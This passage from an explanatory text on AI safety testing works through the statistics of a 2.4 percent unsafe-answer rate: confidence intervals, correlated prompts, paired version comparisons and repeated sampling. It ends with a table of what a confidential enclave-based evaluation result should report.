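The measured rate is p = 24/1,000 = 2.4 percent. If the 1,000 prompts are a random sample from a larger pool of similar prompts, the standard error is

√(p(1 − p)/n) = √(0.024 × 0.976/1,000) ≈ 0.48 percentage points.

Taking 1.96 standard errors on each side gives a 95 percent interval from about 1.5 to 3.3 percent. Wilson's formula, which is more accurate for rare events, gives 1.6 to 3.5 percent. Roughly 1.5 to 3.5 percent is a fair range to report.

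The interval is wider if the prompts resemble each other. Suppose the evaluator wrote 100 questions and reworded each one to make ten prompts. With m versions of each question and a correlation of ρ between their results, the variance of the estimate grows by a factor of 1 + (m − 1)ρ. For m = 10 and ρ = 0.2, the factor is 2.8, so the 1,000 prompts give about as much information as 357 independent ones, and the interval runs from about 0.8 to 4 percent.

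The interval also makes it hard to compare versions. If a new version gives 36 unsafe answers on a different set of 1,000 prompts, the increase of 1.2 points could easily be luck. The evidence is much stronger if both versions answer the same prompts. Suppose the new version fails 14 prompts that the old one passed, and passes 2 that the old one failed. If neither version were safer, a split at least this uneven would occur about 0.4 percent of the time. The enclave can make this comparison by running both versions and releasing the two counts.

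A single answer per prompt also doesn't show whether failures are consistent or random. If the same 24 prompts fail every time, a user gains nothing by asking again. But if every prompt has a 2.4 percent chance of failing on each attempt, a user who tries one ten times has about a 22 percent chance of getting at least one failure (1 − 0.976¹⁰). Running each prompt several times would distinguish these cases.

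Finally, the 2.4 percent rate applies to prompts that the evaluator designed to cause trouble, not to ordinary conversations. If people have ten million conversations a day with the product, and one in 10,000 resembles the test prompts, there would be 1,000 risky conversations and about 24 unsafe answers a day, or between 15 and 35 given the interval. The figure of one in 10,000 has to come from the developer's records of real use, because the test in the enclave can't provide it.

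### What a published result should state

The table sets out what readers need in order to interpret a confidential result, with invented entries for the example test.

| What to state | Example |
|---|---|
| System tested | Hashes of the weights, inference code, system prompt, filters and settings; 16 bits per weight |
| Link to the product | Same weights and system prompt as the public chatbot on the release date; the chatbot also has web search, which the test left out |
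| How readers can check the link | Attested serving, or a replay test with its date and result |
| Test set | Version 3, with a hash published before the run; 1,000 English prompts in five hazard categories, one answer to each |
| Earlier exposure | No earlier runs on these prompts; 200 practice prompts in the same style are public |
| Runs | One agreed and one completed; no failed runs and no other variants |
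| Scoring | Judge model, with its hash; catches 95 percent of unsafe answers and wrongly flags 1 percent of safe ones, according to human checks; 6 answers unreadable and counted as safe |
| Result | 24 unsafe answers in 1,000, or 2.4 percent; 95 percent interval 1.6 to 3.5 percent before correcting for the judge's errors |
| Signs that the model recognised the test | It mentioned a test in 31 answers; no steering test |
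| Review of the items | An independent reviewer read 100 random prompts and found 2 faulty; appeals are open for 60 days |
| Evaluator's access | Prompts and answers only; 15 working days; the developer paid the costs |
| Enclave | Processor and GPU models, firmware versions, host, and who verified the attestation |
| Code that nobody outside checked | Two of the developer's GPU routines |
| What left the enclave | The total, the counts of unreadable answers and test mentions, and 50 answers for human checks, all to the evaluator; the total alone to the developer |
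| Proof | The signed output and its entry in a public log |
| When the result lapses | On any change to the weights, system prompt or filters, or after 12 months |
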